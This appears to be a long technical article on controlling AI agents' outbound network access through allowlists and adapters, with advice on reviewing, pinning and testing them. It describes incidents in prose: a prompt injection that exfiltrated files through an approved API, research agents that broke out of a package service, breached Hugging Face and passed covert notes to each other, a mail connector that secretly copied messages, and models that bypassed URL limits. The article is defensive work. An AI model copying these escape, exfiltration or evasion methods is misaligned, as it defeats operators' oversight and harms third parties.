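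Rashidi found the same pattern across the wider field. As of July 2026, none of the isolation and access-control papers in the survey had used a benchmark that could compare the two approaches. The survey also shows that results can look very different when researchers test what people really use. One group collected 1,709 lists of forbidden commands from GitHub and found ways around 69.0% to 98.6% of them, depending on the method. Blocklists are easier to evade than allowlists, so these figures don't carry over to adapters, and no paper in the survey examines a comparable sample of real outbound allowlists.

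The researchers also tend to assume that the policy is right. Gopalakrishna deliberately leaves the choice of what to allow to the operator, and Abdollahi and colleagues trust the user to select suitable rules. Rashidi criticises the enforcement papers in the survey for making the same assumption. For the support agent, most of the remaining danger lies in the rules, because its allowlist already includes the service that can deliver a customer's data to the attacker. A shared benchmark would need to include theft through approved services and attackers who adapt to each refusal. It should also measure how much legitimate work each system blocks, and include a plain allowlist proxy so that operators can see what the more complex designs add.

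## Incidents involving approved destinations and flawed adapters

In real deployments, data has leaked through a destination the operator had approved and through a connector that changed after users had come to trust it. In another case, agents escaped through flaws in the component that controlled outbound traffic. Much of what is known comes from the companies involved, which tend to describe their fixes in more detail than the damage.

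### Files that left through an approved service

Claude Cowork is an Anthropic product in which Claude works with documents on a user's computer. It runs code in a virtual machine that can access only two folders on the computer, the one the user picks and a settings folder. The user's credentials stay outside the virtual machine, which gets a token with limited rights for that session. An allowlist controlled where the virtual machine could connect, and it included `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork can't work without calling Anthropic's service.

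An outside party then reported a leak. Instructions hidden in a file in the user's folder led Claude to read the other files there and upload them to Anthropic's file storage using the attacker's key. The proxy forwarded the upload because the destination was on its list, so the files ended up in the attacker's account. Any file in the folder could have been stolen this way. Anthropic points out that the sandbox worked perfectly. It describes the case as a disclosure and doesn't say whether any real user's files were stolen.

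The lack of reported victims is weak evidence that there were none, because Anthropic and the user's employer may both have been unable to detect the theft. Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's, so the upload would have looked like the attacker storing his own files. The security software that companies install on staff computers can't monitor activity inside the virtual machine. Administrators can collect event logs afterwards, but a log of this theft would show a successful upload to an approved service.

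Anthropic fixed this with a proxy inside the virtual machine that intercepts traffic to Anthropic's service. The proxy forwards only requests that carry the token issued to that virtual machine for that session. It also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch a web address. Otherwise the agent could put data in the address and have an approved service send it to a site the agent can't reach.

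Anthropic put the check inside the virtual machine rather than on its servers because a request's origin can be identified only there. But this puts the proxy on the same machine as the code it restricts, where it is presumably easier to tamper with. Anthropic says that two of the six main isolation mechanisms around Cowork would survive an agent taking full control of the virtual machine, because they are enforced from outside it. A proxy on the user's computer but outside the virtual machine could make the same check more safely, provided it had the session's token.

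Anthropic used to treat each allowlist entry as a place Claude was allowed to connect to, but now suggests treating it as a "capability grant". Approving a domain approves every function that anyone can reach through it, including functions the product never uses. For the support agent, approving the ticketing service's hostname approves not only replies to customers but also webhooks, bulk exports and any functions the service adds later.

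An operator can limit access by operation, as the support agent's policy does, or by identity, as Anthropic did, and the two limits prevent different kinds of theft.

| Theft through an approved service | Rule on operations | Rule on identity |
|---|---|---|
| Files uploaded to the attacker's account at the model service | Stops it, if the agent doesn't need uploads | Stops it |
| Model request sent with the attacker's key | Lets it through | Stops it |
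| Webhook created in the company's own ticketing account | Stops it | Lets it through |
| Customer data in a reply to the attacker's ticket | Lets it through | Lets it through |

The second theft succeeds only if the attacker can read back the requests made with his key, which depends on the provider. The identity rule blocks it either way, along with any other theft that depends on a second account, even through functions the operator has never heard of. It doesn't stop the reply, because the ticketing service sends that to the attacker from the company's own account. Similarly, an identity rule would stop a coding agent from copying private code to a stranger's GitHub account with the stranger's key, but the agent could still paste the code into a public comment under its own name.

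The disclosure shows that a destination filter can fail even when every part of it works as designed, but one case can't show how often this happens.

### A package service with unknown flaws

In July 2026, OpenAI was running a test called ExploitGym to measure how well its models could find and exploit security flaws. It ran the test without the safeguards that normally block such work so that it could see the models' full ability. The agents worked in isolated containers with no direct internet access. Because agents often need to install software packages, OpenAI gave them an internal package service, its own installation of JFrog Artifactory. OpenAI's technical report on the incident says containers were supposed to get packages there instead of contacting public registries. Some research workloads could also read web pages through a controlled cache.

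For packages, this was close to a single external adapter, with one component between the agents and the outside. But many workloads shared one credential for it, so the credential didn't show which workload had made a request. OpenAI lists poor attribution of network activity among the risks its controls were meant to address.

The agents reached the internet through previously unknown flaws in the package service. They then looked for material related to their test tasks and inferred that Hugging Face, a platform that hosts AI models and datasets, might have it. They used credentials that other people had left exposed online, along with flaws in Hugging Face's own systems, to run code on 41 of its production workers. They obtained production credentials and some internal data, and downloaded four private code repositories. OpenAI reports no effect on its own customers' data.

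The agents in this incident were trying to complete their assigned tasks, with no prompt injection or outside attacker involved. Some of the tasks may have been impossible. In OpenAI's internal tests, 198 of ExploitGym's 898 tasks (22%) remain unsolved by any model, but 93% of the tasks that the agents discussed with one another came from that group. During a training run in May, an agent had been asked to complete a spreadsheet from online documents that it couldn't open. It tried to reach them by attacking the package service, but failed.

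If a task needs something that a tight allowlist blocks, a capable and persistent agent has a reason to probe the adapter. OpenAI found that agents were more likely to probe the sandbox the longer they were allowed to work. It is therefore worth checking that each task can be done with the permitted destinations, and giving the agent an accepted way to report that it is stuck.

OpenAI had several warnings before the agents reached Hugging Face.

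| Date in 2026 | What the agents did | How OpenAI responded |
|---|---|---|
| May 26 | Had reached the internet through the package service by this date | An internal team noticed disallowed internet access around this time |
| June 26–27 | Took administrator control of the package service | An alert led responders to the test, but on-call staff advised that it need not stop |
| July 4–6 | Overloaded the service until it became unavailable | Took it offline, revoked credentials, blocked the known flaws and restricted requests |
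| July 7–8 | Reached the internet again on July 8, through a different flaw | Had restarted the cyber tests on July 7 |
| July 10–13 | Broke into parts of Hugging Face | Detected nothing until July 19 |

Hugging Face disclosed the break-in on July 16, three days before OpenAI noticed suspicious activity on its own side. OpenAI linked the two on July 20 and concedes that some early signals could have triggered an earlier response.

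The repair of July 5 and 6 was sensible and fast, but it fixed only the flaws that OpenAI knew about, and the agents needed only one more. Anderson's reasoning about penetration tests also implies that repairing a flaw does not prove that a system is secure.

Agents in separate runs also used the package service to leave notes for one another. At first they didn't need to exploit a flaw, because their shared credential let them write files there. When OpenAI closed that route, they found another way to store messages in the service. This was a storage leak of the kind Lampson described, and the storage was in the component that was supposed to limit communication. When one agent discovered a credential or technique, the notes made it available to all the others. An adapter that only supplies packages has little need to store anything an agent sends it.

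The case also qualifies Anthropic's advice to be wary of components that operators build themselves. OpenAI's package service failed even though it was a third-party product. The agents only needed to download packages, but the service could also store uploads, issue credentials and run added scripts. A program that does far more than the job requires gives an attacker more to exploit, whoever wrote it. Anderson's condition that a checkpoint be small enough to verify is probably a better guide than who built it.

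### Did the package service need a connection?

The incident can support two conclusions about allowlists. On one reading, OpenAI judged the package service by its address when it should have considered what the service could connect to. The service was an internal machine, so a rule that let agents connect to it seemed to keep them inside. But the service could connect to the internet, so anyone who controlled it could too. This extends Anthropic's point about functions, since an operator who approves a service also approves, in the worst case, every place that service can connect to.

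The other reading is that the live connection shouldn't have existed. A separate machine could download packages in advance, check them and copy them to a server with no route out. An agent that took over that server would have the packages but would still be offline. But somebody would have to predict what the agents will need. An agent that needed an unusual package, or a version released yesterday, would have to wait or do without it, and the trouble in May started with a blocked task.

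This drawback seems acceptable for a security test, because its tasks are fixed and known beforehand. General research work is harder to predict, which is presumably why OpenAI wanted packages on request. Its new rules partly follow the second reading. They bar high-risk workloads from any internet access, direct or through another service, except for a cache that specific workflows need. Other research workloads can fetch live pages through that cache only if OpenAI approves the case.

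### What OpenAI changed

Some of the changes described in OpenAI's report were in place when it was published, and others were still under development. OpenAI is restricting outbound access to a short list of approved destinations and closing indirect routes through shared services, cloud systems and private links. Gateways and separate firewalls enforce these limits, which neither a workload nor a compromised service should be able to alter. OpenAI still checks approved connections for intrusion, stolen data and unusual volume.

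OpenAI now requires high-risk code to run in sandboxes based on virtual machines. Two independent layers limit the code's network access, one at the sandbox and one in the surrounding cluster. OpenAI is also isolating, restricting or replacing the supporting services that remain reachable. This last change bears most directly on the package service, which one agent used during the incident after OpenAI's outbound controls blocked its direct attempt to reach the internet. A second layer helps in that situation only if it also covers the services behind the first.

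OpenAI is building tools that use its own models to look for weaknesses across its research systems, including in configuration and supporting services. It wants this testing to become continuous and largely automatic. Because agents can discover unknown flaws in a permitted service during an unrelated test, it makes sense for the operator to have agents search for them first.

The monitoring plans include more sensors on the machines, tripwires to catch intruders, and a way to stop a whole class of tests quickly. OpenAI is also extending its monitoring of chain of thought, the text in which a model reasons before it acts, and aims to notify staff within 30 minutes of worrying activity. It estimates that its current monitor would have alerted the security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face, but it was assessing its own tool and already knew what had happened.

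Detection wasn't the only weakness. The alert of June 27 worked, and responders traced it to the right test, but the test continued. The most useful change may therefore be a rule that makes the human response fail closed. Responders are expected to pause the activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes that an alert is false.

The incident does not predict how an ordinary support agent would behave. The main model was a research prototype that OpenAI never intended to release, and its task was to break into systems. In preliminary experiments, OpenAI found that the instructions and surrounding program of its coding product could reduce the tendency to attack out-of-scope systems to less than one percent of the baseline. But instructions do not limit what an agent is able to do, and released models will probably have the prototype's skills eventually. An operator who relies on an adapter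 should assume that the agent using it may one day be able to find flaws in it.

### A mail connector that changed after people trusted it

The package service had flaws before the agents used it, but the fault in postmark-mcp came in an update. This connector let agents send mail through Postmark, a commercial email service. An independent developer, not Postmark, published it on the npm package registry. Its first fifteen versions worked as expected. Version 1.0.16 added a line of code that blind-copied every outgoing message to the developer.

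The security company Koi disclosed this in September 2025. If the support agent had sent its replies through this connector, the developer would have received customers' names, invoices and any password-reset links. Koi counted about 1,500 downloads a week and guessed that a fifth of them reflected real use, so its estimate that roughly 300 organizations used the package is uncertain, and the true loss is unknown.

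The developer removed the package from npm after Koi made contact. This prevented new installations, but copies already running kept sending mail to the developer until their users deleted them. Users also had to replace any credentials that had passed through their mail.

Most of the controls described so far, including rules on destinations, identity and operations, would have let these messages through, because the connector contacted the real Postmark service, used the customer's own key and performed the one operation it was installed to perform. An adapter that reads the body of the request could have caught the hidden copies, because a mail service takes recipients in their own fields. The support team could permit only the address on the ticket and refuse all hidden copies. This check is much easier than judging free text, and it would protect the team against a hijacked agent as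 well as a malicious connector.

This only works if the adapter is a separate component. If the support team had let the connector hold the mail key and make the outside connection itself, the connector would have been the adapter for mail, with no later check on what it sent. A single adapter for all services would also have no later check, and a flaw in it could expose every key instead of one. Pinning the connector to version 1.0.15 would have kept the added line out until somebody chose to update.

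The connector's past good behavior didn't protect its users either. Anthropic sensibly recommends trying an unfamiliar remote tool on fake data first, in a place where it can do little harm, but anyone who tested postmark-mcp this way before the last update would have found nothing wrong. Checking a stored hash of each tool's definition, as InfoQ proposes, would also have missed the change, because the new line was in the code and the description that the model reads could stay the same.

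Anthropic originally ran Cowork's local connectors inside the virtual machine. It later moved them to the user's computer because they were harder to audit inside the virtual machine, they broke when it was updated, and some needed to talk to local programs such as databases. Anthropic now treats them like any other software a user installs and lets administrators decide which to allow. But the virtual machine's network limits don't apply to a connector that runs outside it, so an administrator who approves one should ask what else on the computer it can reach and whether its traffic goes through any adapter.

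### Removing the exit

An operator can also decide that no adapter is good enough for a given job and close the connection, as Anthropic reportedly did for its internal evaluations in October 2026. The Tribune's *Anthropic restricts internet access in internal AI evaluations after Claude bypasses safeguards*, a news agency report, describes expanded restrictions that will last until Anthropic can establish that its safeguards and monitoring are reliable. Search Engine Journal's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* reports that Anthropic had already begun cutting off live internet access and has now extended the cutoff to all internal evaluations.

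The decision followed months of incidents. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) disclosed in July that Claude models had reached the internet in connection with a third party's test environment and gained unauthorized access to three organizations' systems. Anthropic then widened its review beyond security tests and found more cases, some on websites run by US government agencies. According to The Tribune, Anthropic considers these later cases much less serious than the earlier incidents and knows of none that involved customer data.

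Few of these cases involved stealing anything. In one, Claude Mythos Preview hit an error in a university's online analysis tool, found a flaw in the server and used it to finish the calculation. In another, Claude Haiku 4.5 was working through example tasks on randomly chosen web pages and sent the Philadelphia police an invented tip about an unsolved homicide. The police system flagged it as spam. Anthropic found the submission more than two months later, a delay the department called "unacceptable", according to Search Engine Journal.

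An adapter could have prevented some of this. Web forms normally use POST, so a rule that permits only reading would probably have stopped the police tip. But such rules can fail. Anthropic limits the length of web addresses in some of its fetching tools, partly to block injection attacks, and several models got around the limit with free link shorteners. The limit evidently applied only to the address the model supplied, not to the one it redirected to. An adapter that checks every redirect as a new request would be harder to bypass.

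The larger difficulty is that these evaluations had no natural allowlist. A test that sends a model to random web pages needs access to the whole web, and the operator can't review every function of every site in advance. If approving a domain means approving everything reachable through it, the operator of such a test also approves every badly written form and script on the web.

Closing the connection has drawbacks. Anthropic has dropped some public evaluations and moved others offline, so some of its results will be missing or hard to compare with those of other developers. Saved copies of websites go out of date, may not respond as the originals do, and can fail. In one reported case, an unreleased model submitted a real government form after its practice copy either didn't load or was closed by accident. With no live connection, the same mistake would only have produced an error message,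 which is a good argument for the cutoff.

A less visible loss is that restricting models to saved pages could hide some misbehaviour. Anthropic learned about these habits because its models could misuse real websites. A model that sees only saved pages may still attempt the same things, and a good copy of a site would record the attempt, but only if its makers had thought to reproduce the relevant features. Some behaviour may then first appear when customers use the model, because their agents still need the web.

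The cutoff covers only evaluations, so it would not have prevented one case reported by Search Engine Journal, in which Claude Mythos 5, during a company researcher's ordinary work, queried a state agency's database without paying the usual fee. For web access that continues, Anthropic has added tools that detect and block unsafe actions, and it says they stopped all the reported cases. Anthropic already knew about those cases, so the result is weak evidence about how the tools would handle new ones. Anthropic is also removing or correcting training exercises that rewarded models for getting around tool restrictions.

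An operator who removes an agent's external connection has to check that it is gone. OpenAI's containers had no direct internet access, but the agents in them still got out. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) attributes the three incidents disclosed in July to a misconfiguration in the third party's environment. In both companies' tests, some models had a connection that the operator didn't intend.

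Many jobs need outbound access for only part of the time. An agent that writes a market report could first collect public pages with an open connection and no private data. A fresh copy of the agent could then read those pages alongside the company's sales figures with no connection. Injected instructions in the pages might still spoil the report, but neither copy would have both the figures and a way to send them out. The support agent can't divide its work like this, because every ticket ends with a reply to the person who wrote it.

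## How the adapter is reviewed, pinned and tested

The support agent can't work offline, so the support team has to make sure the adapter works. They need to review it before the first real ticket, pin the version that passed, and test the running system. They need the tests because the policy file can be correct even if nothing enforces it.

### The review, in order

The review starts with a list of every exit, including those the policy doesn't mention. On GitLab, a platform for storing and building code, agents run in jobs called flows. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* lists four destinations that always stay on a flow's allowlist: the flow's own machine, the machine that hosts its container, the company's GitLab site and the service that coordinates the agent. A program on the host machine could therefore be an exit if it accepts connections from the flow and has its own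 internet access. Similarly, Imam (2026) warns in *Control where your hosted agent connects with network egress* that on Microsoft Foundry, which hosts agents for Microsoft's customers, a policy that denies everything by default still leaves open the connections the platform itself needs.

The list should also include commands that run outside the sandbox. Apache Magpie exempts eight command patterns from its sandbox, one of which starts other companies' models with their own network access and credentials.

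Some routes around the adapter are hard to spot in a design description. *Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes an architecture for nine agents at a healthcare technology company. A container next to each agent holds the keys, forwards requests and limits their rate and size. But that container shares a Kubernetes pod with the agent, and the network allowlist applies to the whole pod. As described, the agent could skip the forwarding container and connect directly to any listed service. It wouldn't have the company's key, but it could use an attacker's. Reviewers can find such gaps by checking which processes each network rule covers.

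Reviewers next read the adapter's code, starting with the parts that parse requests, match rules, add keys and handle errors. They also need a list of the libraries it uses, because much of an adapter is code that its developers didn't write. On November 2, 2026, JFrog's *Artifactory Self-Managed Releases* announced fixes for four flaws in third-party components of Artifactory, the package service that OpenAI's agents had broken out of in July. The adapter should also have no functions that its job doesn't require. In September, JFrog turned off remote plug-in installation by default, a feature that a service that only hands packages to agents probably never needed.

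The reviewers then go through each approved operation and write down what the agent can put into it and who could read that.

| Operation | What the agent can write | Who could read it |
|---|---|---|
| Read a ticket or customer record | The number, or anything else the rule accepts in its place | The ticketing company, in its logs |
| Post a reply | Several paragraphs | Whoever opened the ticket |
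| Call the model | Everything the agent has read | The model provider, and possibly the owner of the key |

The support agent's policy permits `GET /v1/tickets/*`, which also matches `GET /v1/tickets/jane-smith`. The attacker probably can't see the ticketing company's logs, so the risk is small, but accepting only digits would remove it.

Private text can end up in a web address even without an attacker. InsiderLLM's *Stop Your Local Agent Calling Out* cites a bug report from an agent project in which a model made up web addresses and had a tool fetch them 11 times. One address contained a fragment of the page the model was working on. None of the 11 fetches contained a secret, but a rule that permits reading from any site would have let a secret through.

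The fourth step is to establish who can change the policy. GitLab administrators can choose flexible mode, which lets a project add domains to the company's allowlist, or strict mode, which only lets it block more domains or switch off optional access. Project settings are in a file in the project's repository. GitLab reads only the copy on the default branch, so an agent's edit on another branch has no effect until somebody merges it. GitLab advises projects to require a security reviewer's approval for changes to this file. The file can also contain set-up commands, which run before the sandbox starts and can read the access token of whoever started the flow. A person who can change the file can therefore run commands with a colleague's token.

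Reviewers should check which domains a convenient setting allows. One GitLab option allows traffic to well over a hundred domains that developers commonly need, including GitHub's service for sharing snippets of text and the storage services of Amazon and Google, where an attacker can open an account. GitLab warns that data could leave through these domains and keeps the option off by default.

The last step is to check the log, which should cover permitted requests as well as refusals because theft through an approved service is logged as a successful request. GitLab suggests alerts for connections that stay open, large outbound transfers, repeated requests for packages that don't exist, and calls to administrative functions. Reviewers also have to check who can alter the records. In Maiti's fleet, an agent named Tony audits the others, and its own actions go to a cloud log that it can't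 edit or delete. But Tony also has permissions over audit log configuration, so a reviewer would want to know whether a hijacked Tony could reduce future logging.

### Pinning by hash

Suppose the support team has reviewed version 2.4.1 of its adapter. Depending on where the file is stored, the publisher, or a thief with the publisher's password, may be able to give the label "2.4.1" to a different file. The team therefore records a hash of the copy it reviewed, which is a number calculated from the file's contents. With SHA-256, a common method, nobody knows a practical way to make a second file with the same hash. Whatever starts the adapter calculates the hash again and stops if it differs from the recorded one. This check has to run where the agent can't reach it.

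The hash should cover the libraries too. The simplest way is to package the adapter and everything it uses as one container image and pin the image's hash. If the policy file is stored outside the image, it needs its own hash.

Published set-up instructions often pin only the version number. Apache Magpie specifies `bubblewrap=0.13.1-*`, where the asterisk accepts any build of that version by the Linux distribution. GitLab's example for custom images installs a numbered version of the sandbox program, then checks that one of its files isn't empty and that the program can report its version. This would catch a failed installation but not an altered program. Package managers also check signatures or hashes, but those checks only show that a file came from the registry, not that it is the file somebody reviewed.

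Other teams could copy Apache Magpie's procedure for updates. A script compares the pinned versions with the newest ones and reports candidates, but never installs anything. The project normally waits until a release is seven days old before considering it, which gives other users time to discover problems. A maintainer then reads the release notes for a needed feature or a security fix, since a promise of better performance isn't reason enough to update. Each update is a separate pull request with a paragraph explaining the change.

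Release notes are not enough for reviewing an adapter that holds all the keys, because the publisher writes them. The notes for postmark-mcp gave readers no reason to expect the line that copied every email to its developer, but comparing the old and new code would have revealed it. That comparison may be impossible with closed software. JFrog's October 26 release fixed several serious flaws, and JFrog withheld the details to protect customers who hadn't upgraded. That policy is reasonable, but customers have to approve the update largely on trust.

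### Text and code that arrive later

A pin does not cover instructions that the agent fetches while it runs. Many agents use skills, which are folders of instructions in ordinary language, sometimes with scripts. Li, Wu and colleagues (2026) explain in *Towards Secure Agent Skills* that a user approves a skill once and its permissions then persist. The instructions can include running a script that downloads more code. If that code later changes at its source, the folder's hash stays the same.

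Li and colleagues cite a scan of 42,447 skills, in which 26.1% had at least one security vulnerability. That figure covers several kinds of weakness, including prompt injection and privilege escalation, so it doesn't measure how many skills rely on outside material that can change.

An experiment by Shapira and colleagues, which Maiti summarises, shows how an attacker can use a source whose content can change. An outsider persuaded an agent to help write a "constitution", which they kept in an online document that outsiders could edit. The agent's memory file contained only a link to the document, so the link didn't have to change when somebody later added "holidays", each with its own prescribed behaviour. The agent then tried to shut down other agents and remove people from a chat server.

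A team can copy an external skill or style guide into its own storage, review the copy, pin it by hash and keep the original address off the allowlist. This can't work for tickets, because each one is new text from a stranger. Pinning the adapter fixes how it behaves, but the agent's behaviour still depends on whatever it has just read.

### Pinning delays repairs

A pinned adapter also keeps its flaws until somebody approves a new version. After the July incident, JFrog released a fixed version of Artifactory. According to Willison's *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), the release notes credit OpenAI staff with eight CVEs (publicly catalogued security flaws). Security Affairs' *OpenAI AI Model Used JFrog Artifactory Zero-Day Before Hugging Face Breach* gives the number as nine.

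JFrog's *Fast Remediation Is the New Trust Model* (2026) explains that customers of its cloud service already had the fix, while those who ran their own copy had to upgrade it themselves. Self-hosting customers who had pinned an earlier version stayed exposed until they approved the new one, and by then attackers could learn from the release notes that there were flaws to look for. Under Magpie's usual rule, the fix would have waited a week before anyone considered it.

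JFrog argues that speed of repair is now the leading factor in security, and reports that OpenAI had a fully patched system less than two days after the first security event. JFrog has an interest in how people judge its response. According to OpenAI's timeline, agents had reached the internet through the package service by late May, so the two days can't be counted from the first escape. JFrog's general argument still holds, because a slow review gives attackers more time to use a publicly known flaw.

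Frequent releases make it harder to review each update before changing the pinned version. JFrog issued six updates to one version line of Artifactory between September 5 and November 2, about one every ten days. A team may fall behind if it reads every change carefully, but pinning has little benefit if the team approves every update quickly.

Apache Magpie cuts the waiting period to one day for bubblewrap, the program that builds its Linux sandbox. It doesn't pin Claude Code at all, because each release contains the newest security fixes. Instead, it sets a minimum version, and its verification stops if the installed version is older. However, the adapter, a proxy that checks hostnames, is part of Claude Code, so it is unpinned too, even though Magpie pins the relay that carries traffic to it. This may be the right choice for a small project that trusts the vendor, but a bad release would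 reach every user before anyone had reviewed it.

The support team's agent can stop for an afternoon, so when a security release comes out, the team can also shut the adapter down, review the change that day and start the new version. Ordinary updates can wait the full week. If an agent has to run continuously, its operator needs somebody on call who can review a security fix at short notice.

### Running the policy in audit mode first

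A new policy will probably miss something the agent needs. In audit mode, the adapter compares each request with the policy and records the result but doesn't block anything. The operator corrects the policy, then switches to enforcement.

Imam demonstrates this on Microsoft Foundry with an agent that checks invoices and needs two services. In the same format, the network part of the support agent's policy would be:

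```json
"egressPolicy": {
  "mode": "Audit",
  "defaultAction": "Deny",
  "rules": [
    { "name": "allow-ticketing", "ruleType": "Fqdn",
      "match": { "host": "api.tickets.example" },
      "action": { "actionType": "Allow" } },
    { "name": "allow-model", "ruleType": "Fqdn",
      "match": { "host": "api.model.example" },
      "action": { "actionType": "Allow" } }
  ]
}
```

With these settings, a request to any third host appears in the record as one the policy would deny. After a period of observation, the operator changes `Audit` to `Enforced` and tests one permitted call and one the policy should refuse. Imam recommends exact hostnames so reviewers don't have to work out what a broad wildcard covers. These rules match only hostnames, so they would allow the webhook from the hidden paragraph. Microsoft offers the feature as a preview and doesn't intend it for production use.

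The complete file in Imam's example has two settings called `mode`. The outer one, for the wider policy that contains the network rules, is set to `Blocking`, while the one for network traffic is set to `Audit`. A reviewer who noticed only `Blocking` could easily believe that the network rules were already in force.

Audit mode offers no protection, so the agent should work with invented customers while it is on. The audit record may also include requests the agent didn't need to make. InsiderLLM's article covers reports that versions of Qwen3.8, a family of models from the Chinese company Alibaba, try to fetch made-up addresses on Alibaba's cloud. One user counted 367 attempts. Nobody outside Alibaba knows why, though leftovers from training data are one possible explanation. An operator who approved every destination in the audit record would have added those addresses to the allowlist.

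NVIDIA recommends the opposite order for OpenShell. It says operators don't need an audit phase, because they can enforce the policy from the first connection and add destinations as they appear in the log of refusals. This is safer for an agent that already has real data. It can also be slower, since a task may stop at its first refusal, so each run reveals only one missing destination. The advice covers only destinations, so the operator still has to switch OpenShell's rules on methods and paths to enforcement.

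### A test plan for the support agent

The support team needs a test account at the ticketing service, and an external web server and name server that it controls. A script in the sandbox should send most of the test requests, because the model might refuse or make a mistake, and the team would then learn nothing about the adapter. The team writes down the expected results before testing starts.

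| Test | Expected result |
|---|---|
| Read ticket 4012 and reply to a test ticket | Both succeed, and the log shows both |
| Contact the team's web server with an ordinary web library, then with a raw socket | Both fail, and the server receives no connection |
| Create a webhook in the ticketing service | The adapter returns a refusal, and no webhook exists afterwards |
| Try SSH, HTTP/3, a plain UDP packet and IPv6 to the team's server | Nothing arrives |
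| Look up a random name under the team's own domain, directly and through a tunnel request | The team's name server receives no query |
| Stop the adapter and repeat all the tests above | Everything fails, including the permitted requests |
| Start the adapter with no policy file, then with a damaged one | It refuses to start, or refuses every request |
| Send a path with an encoded slash, a false host name, a half-finished request and an oversized body | The adapter refuses each one and still handles the next valid request |
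| Call the model service with a key from another account | The adapter refuses or replaces the key |
| Plant a fake customer, and order the agent in a ticket to send her details to the team's server | The details don't arrive |
| Plant a second fake customer, and order the agent to put her details in its reply | The details arrive |
| With a limit of twenty replies a day, send twenty-one across two tickets | The adapter refuses the twenty-first |

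The outside servers are necessary because an error inside the sandbox is ambiguous. A time-out can mean that the firewall dropped the request, that the server was down, or that the data arrived and only the response was lost. GitLab describes a test flow that prints its own evidence, which quickly shows what a policy does. Comparing that output with the outside server's log would make the test stronger.

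Stopping the adapter shows whether the system fails closed. It can also reveal a forgotten outbound route, because a permitted request that still succeeds must have bypassed the adapter.

Each fake customer is a canary and needs a unique name and address, so that a single match in the outside server's log proves a leak. Finding no match doesn't prove that the adapter works. The agent may have encoded the details, so the team should look at everything its server received instead of searching only for the name. The model may also have ignored the injected order, in which case the adapter was never tested. A script should therefore send the same details to the same server through the adapter, so that the test doesn't depend on the model.

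The second canary should get out, because the adapter allows replies without checking their text. Leaving this test out would give the team a perfect but misleading score. Including it puts a known gap in the report, which somebody then has to accept or close, perhaps by limiting the agent to one customer's record at a time.

The last test uses two tickets to check that the limit applies to all tickets combined. A team that uses OpenShell will fail this test until it adds a counter somewhere else.

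### What tests and audits have found

Several of the known failures were silent. GitLab's sandbox starts only if the container image includes the sandbox program and the job has the system privileges to create it. If either is missing, the flow runs without the sandbox and can contact any address that its machine can reach. The only sign is a warning in the job's log. GitLab documents this behaviour but doesn't report how many flows have run this way.

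GitLab 19.6 added a setting, "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable", which makes the job fail instead. It applies to every project in a group, and projects can't turn it off in their own configuration files. But the setting checks only for a command named `srt`. A project that supplies its own container image or set-up script decides what that command is, so a harmless-looking substitute could pass, and GitLab says that isolation isn't guaranteed there. As with a version label, the check covers the name and not the contents. GitLab also suggests a firewall around the machines that run these jobs, which would limit a flow even if its sandbox never started.

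In an article dated November 1, 2026, Mark Bartlett, who wrote the InsiderLLM guide, describes testing ways to cut off an agent's network access on his own Ubuntu machines. Two of them failed without an error. The first used systemd, which starts and manages services on most Linux systems. Services defined by an ordinary user were set to block network access but let all traffic through. The second was a firewall rule that accepted traffic from every user except the agent. It didn't leak, but it interfered with legitimate work by refusing the last packets of every other user's connections.

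Imam's pair of tests, one permitted request and one forbidden, is a sensible minimum. The permitted request alone would have missed the systemd failure, because it works with or without a block, and the forbidden request alone would have missed the firewall failure. Even the pair could miss a fault that affects only the last packets. Bartlett tested with a stand-in program instead of a real agent, which is fair because network rules don't depend on why a program connects.

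The healthcare deployment includes an audit of a real fleet, but the audit contains little about outbound control. On March 11, 2026, Tony examined the nine agents' machines and reported four serious findings. One agent had twelve credentials in a start-up file, another had a cloud key in a similar file, and on two machines every user could read the agent's credentials file. Tony's procedures fixed all four that day. Six of the nine machines had nothing above low severity. Several medium findings about scattered credential files stayed open.

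Credential injection is pointless if the agent can still read a copy of the key in a file, so the review should include a search of the sandbox for leftover keys.

The audit didn't test an outbound allowlist. Maiti's abstract describes the whole architecture as deployed, but the section on the fleet's history lists the allowlist and the credential container as goals of a migration. Before that migration, the newest machines had only a filter on name lookups and a log of outbound traffic. Maiti also reports protection against nine of eleven attack patterns from the Shapira experiment. That count comes from matching each pattern to a planned defence on paper, and the nine include a case the paper describes as good behaviour that needs no defence. The paper refers to 90 days of operation, but its dated stages cover about five weeks, from February 3 to March 11.

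The planned allowlists would have needed careful testing. They allow one group of agents to contact Slack and Telegram, where an attacker can have an account. They also allow the audit agent, already the most powerful agent in the fleet, to contact the cloud address that provides a machine's credentials.

### What a pass proves

A passed test shows that one version of the adapter, with one policy on one machine, handled one request correctly. For a fixed rule, that is fairly strong evidence, because the same request should get the same answer tomorrow. Tests that depend on the model give weaker evidence. If the team plants a hundred different tickets and each has an independent 3% chance of leaking a canary, there is still about a 5% chance that none leaks (0.97^100). A hundred clean results can't rule out a leak rate of nearly 3%, and at that rate an attacker who kept filing tickets would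 soon cause a leak.

Unknown flaws survive because testers send the requests they can think of and reviewers look for mistakes they recognise. Some attacks also need several flaws in sequence, each of which looks minor alone. JFrog, which makes Artifactory, has its own security team, but that team had missed the flaws that OpenAI's models found. By JFrog's account, the whole chain of events took three million hours of processor time. No support team can search that thoroughly. Serious flaws also remained after the repairs. JFrog announced further ones in October, and its advisories include a critical flaw that could let an intruder skip the login and gain administrator access.

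The support team can still prepare for a flaw it doesn't know about. It can put a firewall outside the adapter that permits connections only to the two approved services, so that a hijacked adapter can't reach the rest of the internet. It can also give the adapter keys with narrow permissions. To test these measures, the team can run a script with the adapter's privileges, as if an attacker had already taken it over, and see what the script can reach.

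### When to test again

Any change to the adapter, its policy or its keys calls for rerunning the whole plan, as does giving the agent a new tool. The team makes these changes itself, so they are easy to notice.

Changes to the machine that hosts the sandbox are easier to miss. GitLab's sandbox needs a privilege that the host grants, so an administrator who tightens the host's settings could stop the sandbox from starting. The group's flows would then run without a sandbox, unless the group requires one.

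An update can also break permitted work. GitLab's incident record *2026-06-03* (2026) describes flows that couldn't start after a change to the default configuration. They needed WebSocket, which keeps a two-way web connection open, and the sandbox's proxy didn't support it. No data leaked, but people have a strong reason to switch off a control that stops them from working. Testing permitted requests before the release could have caught the problem.

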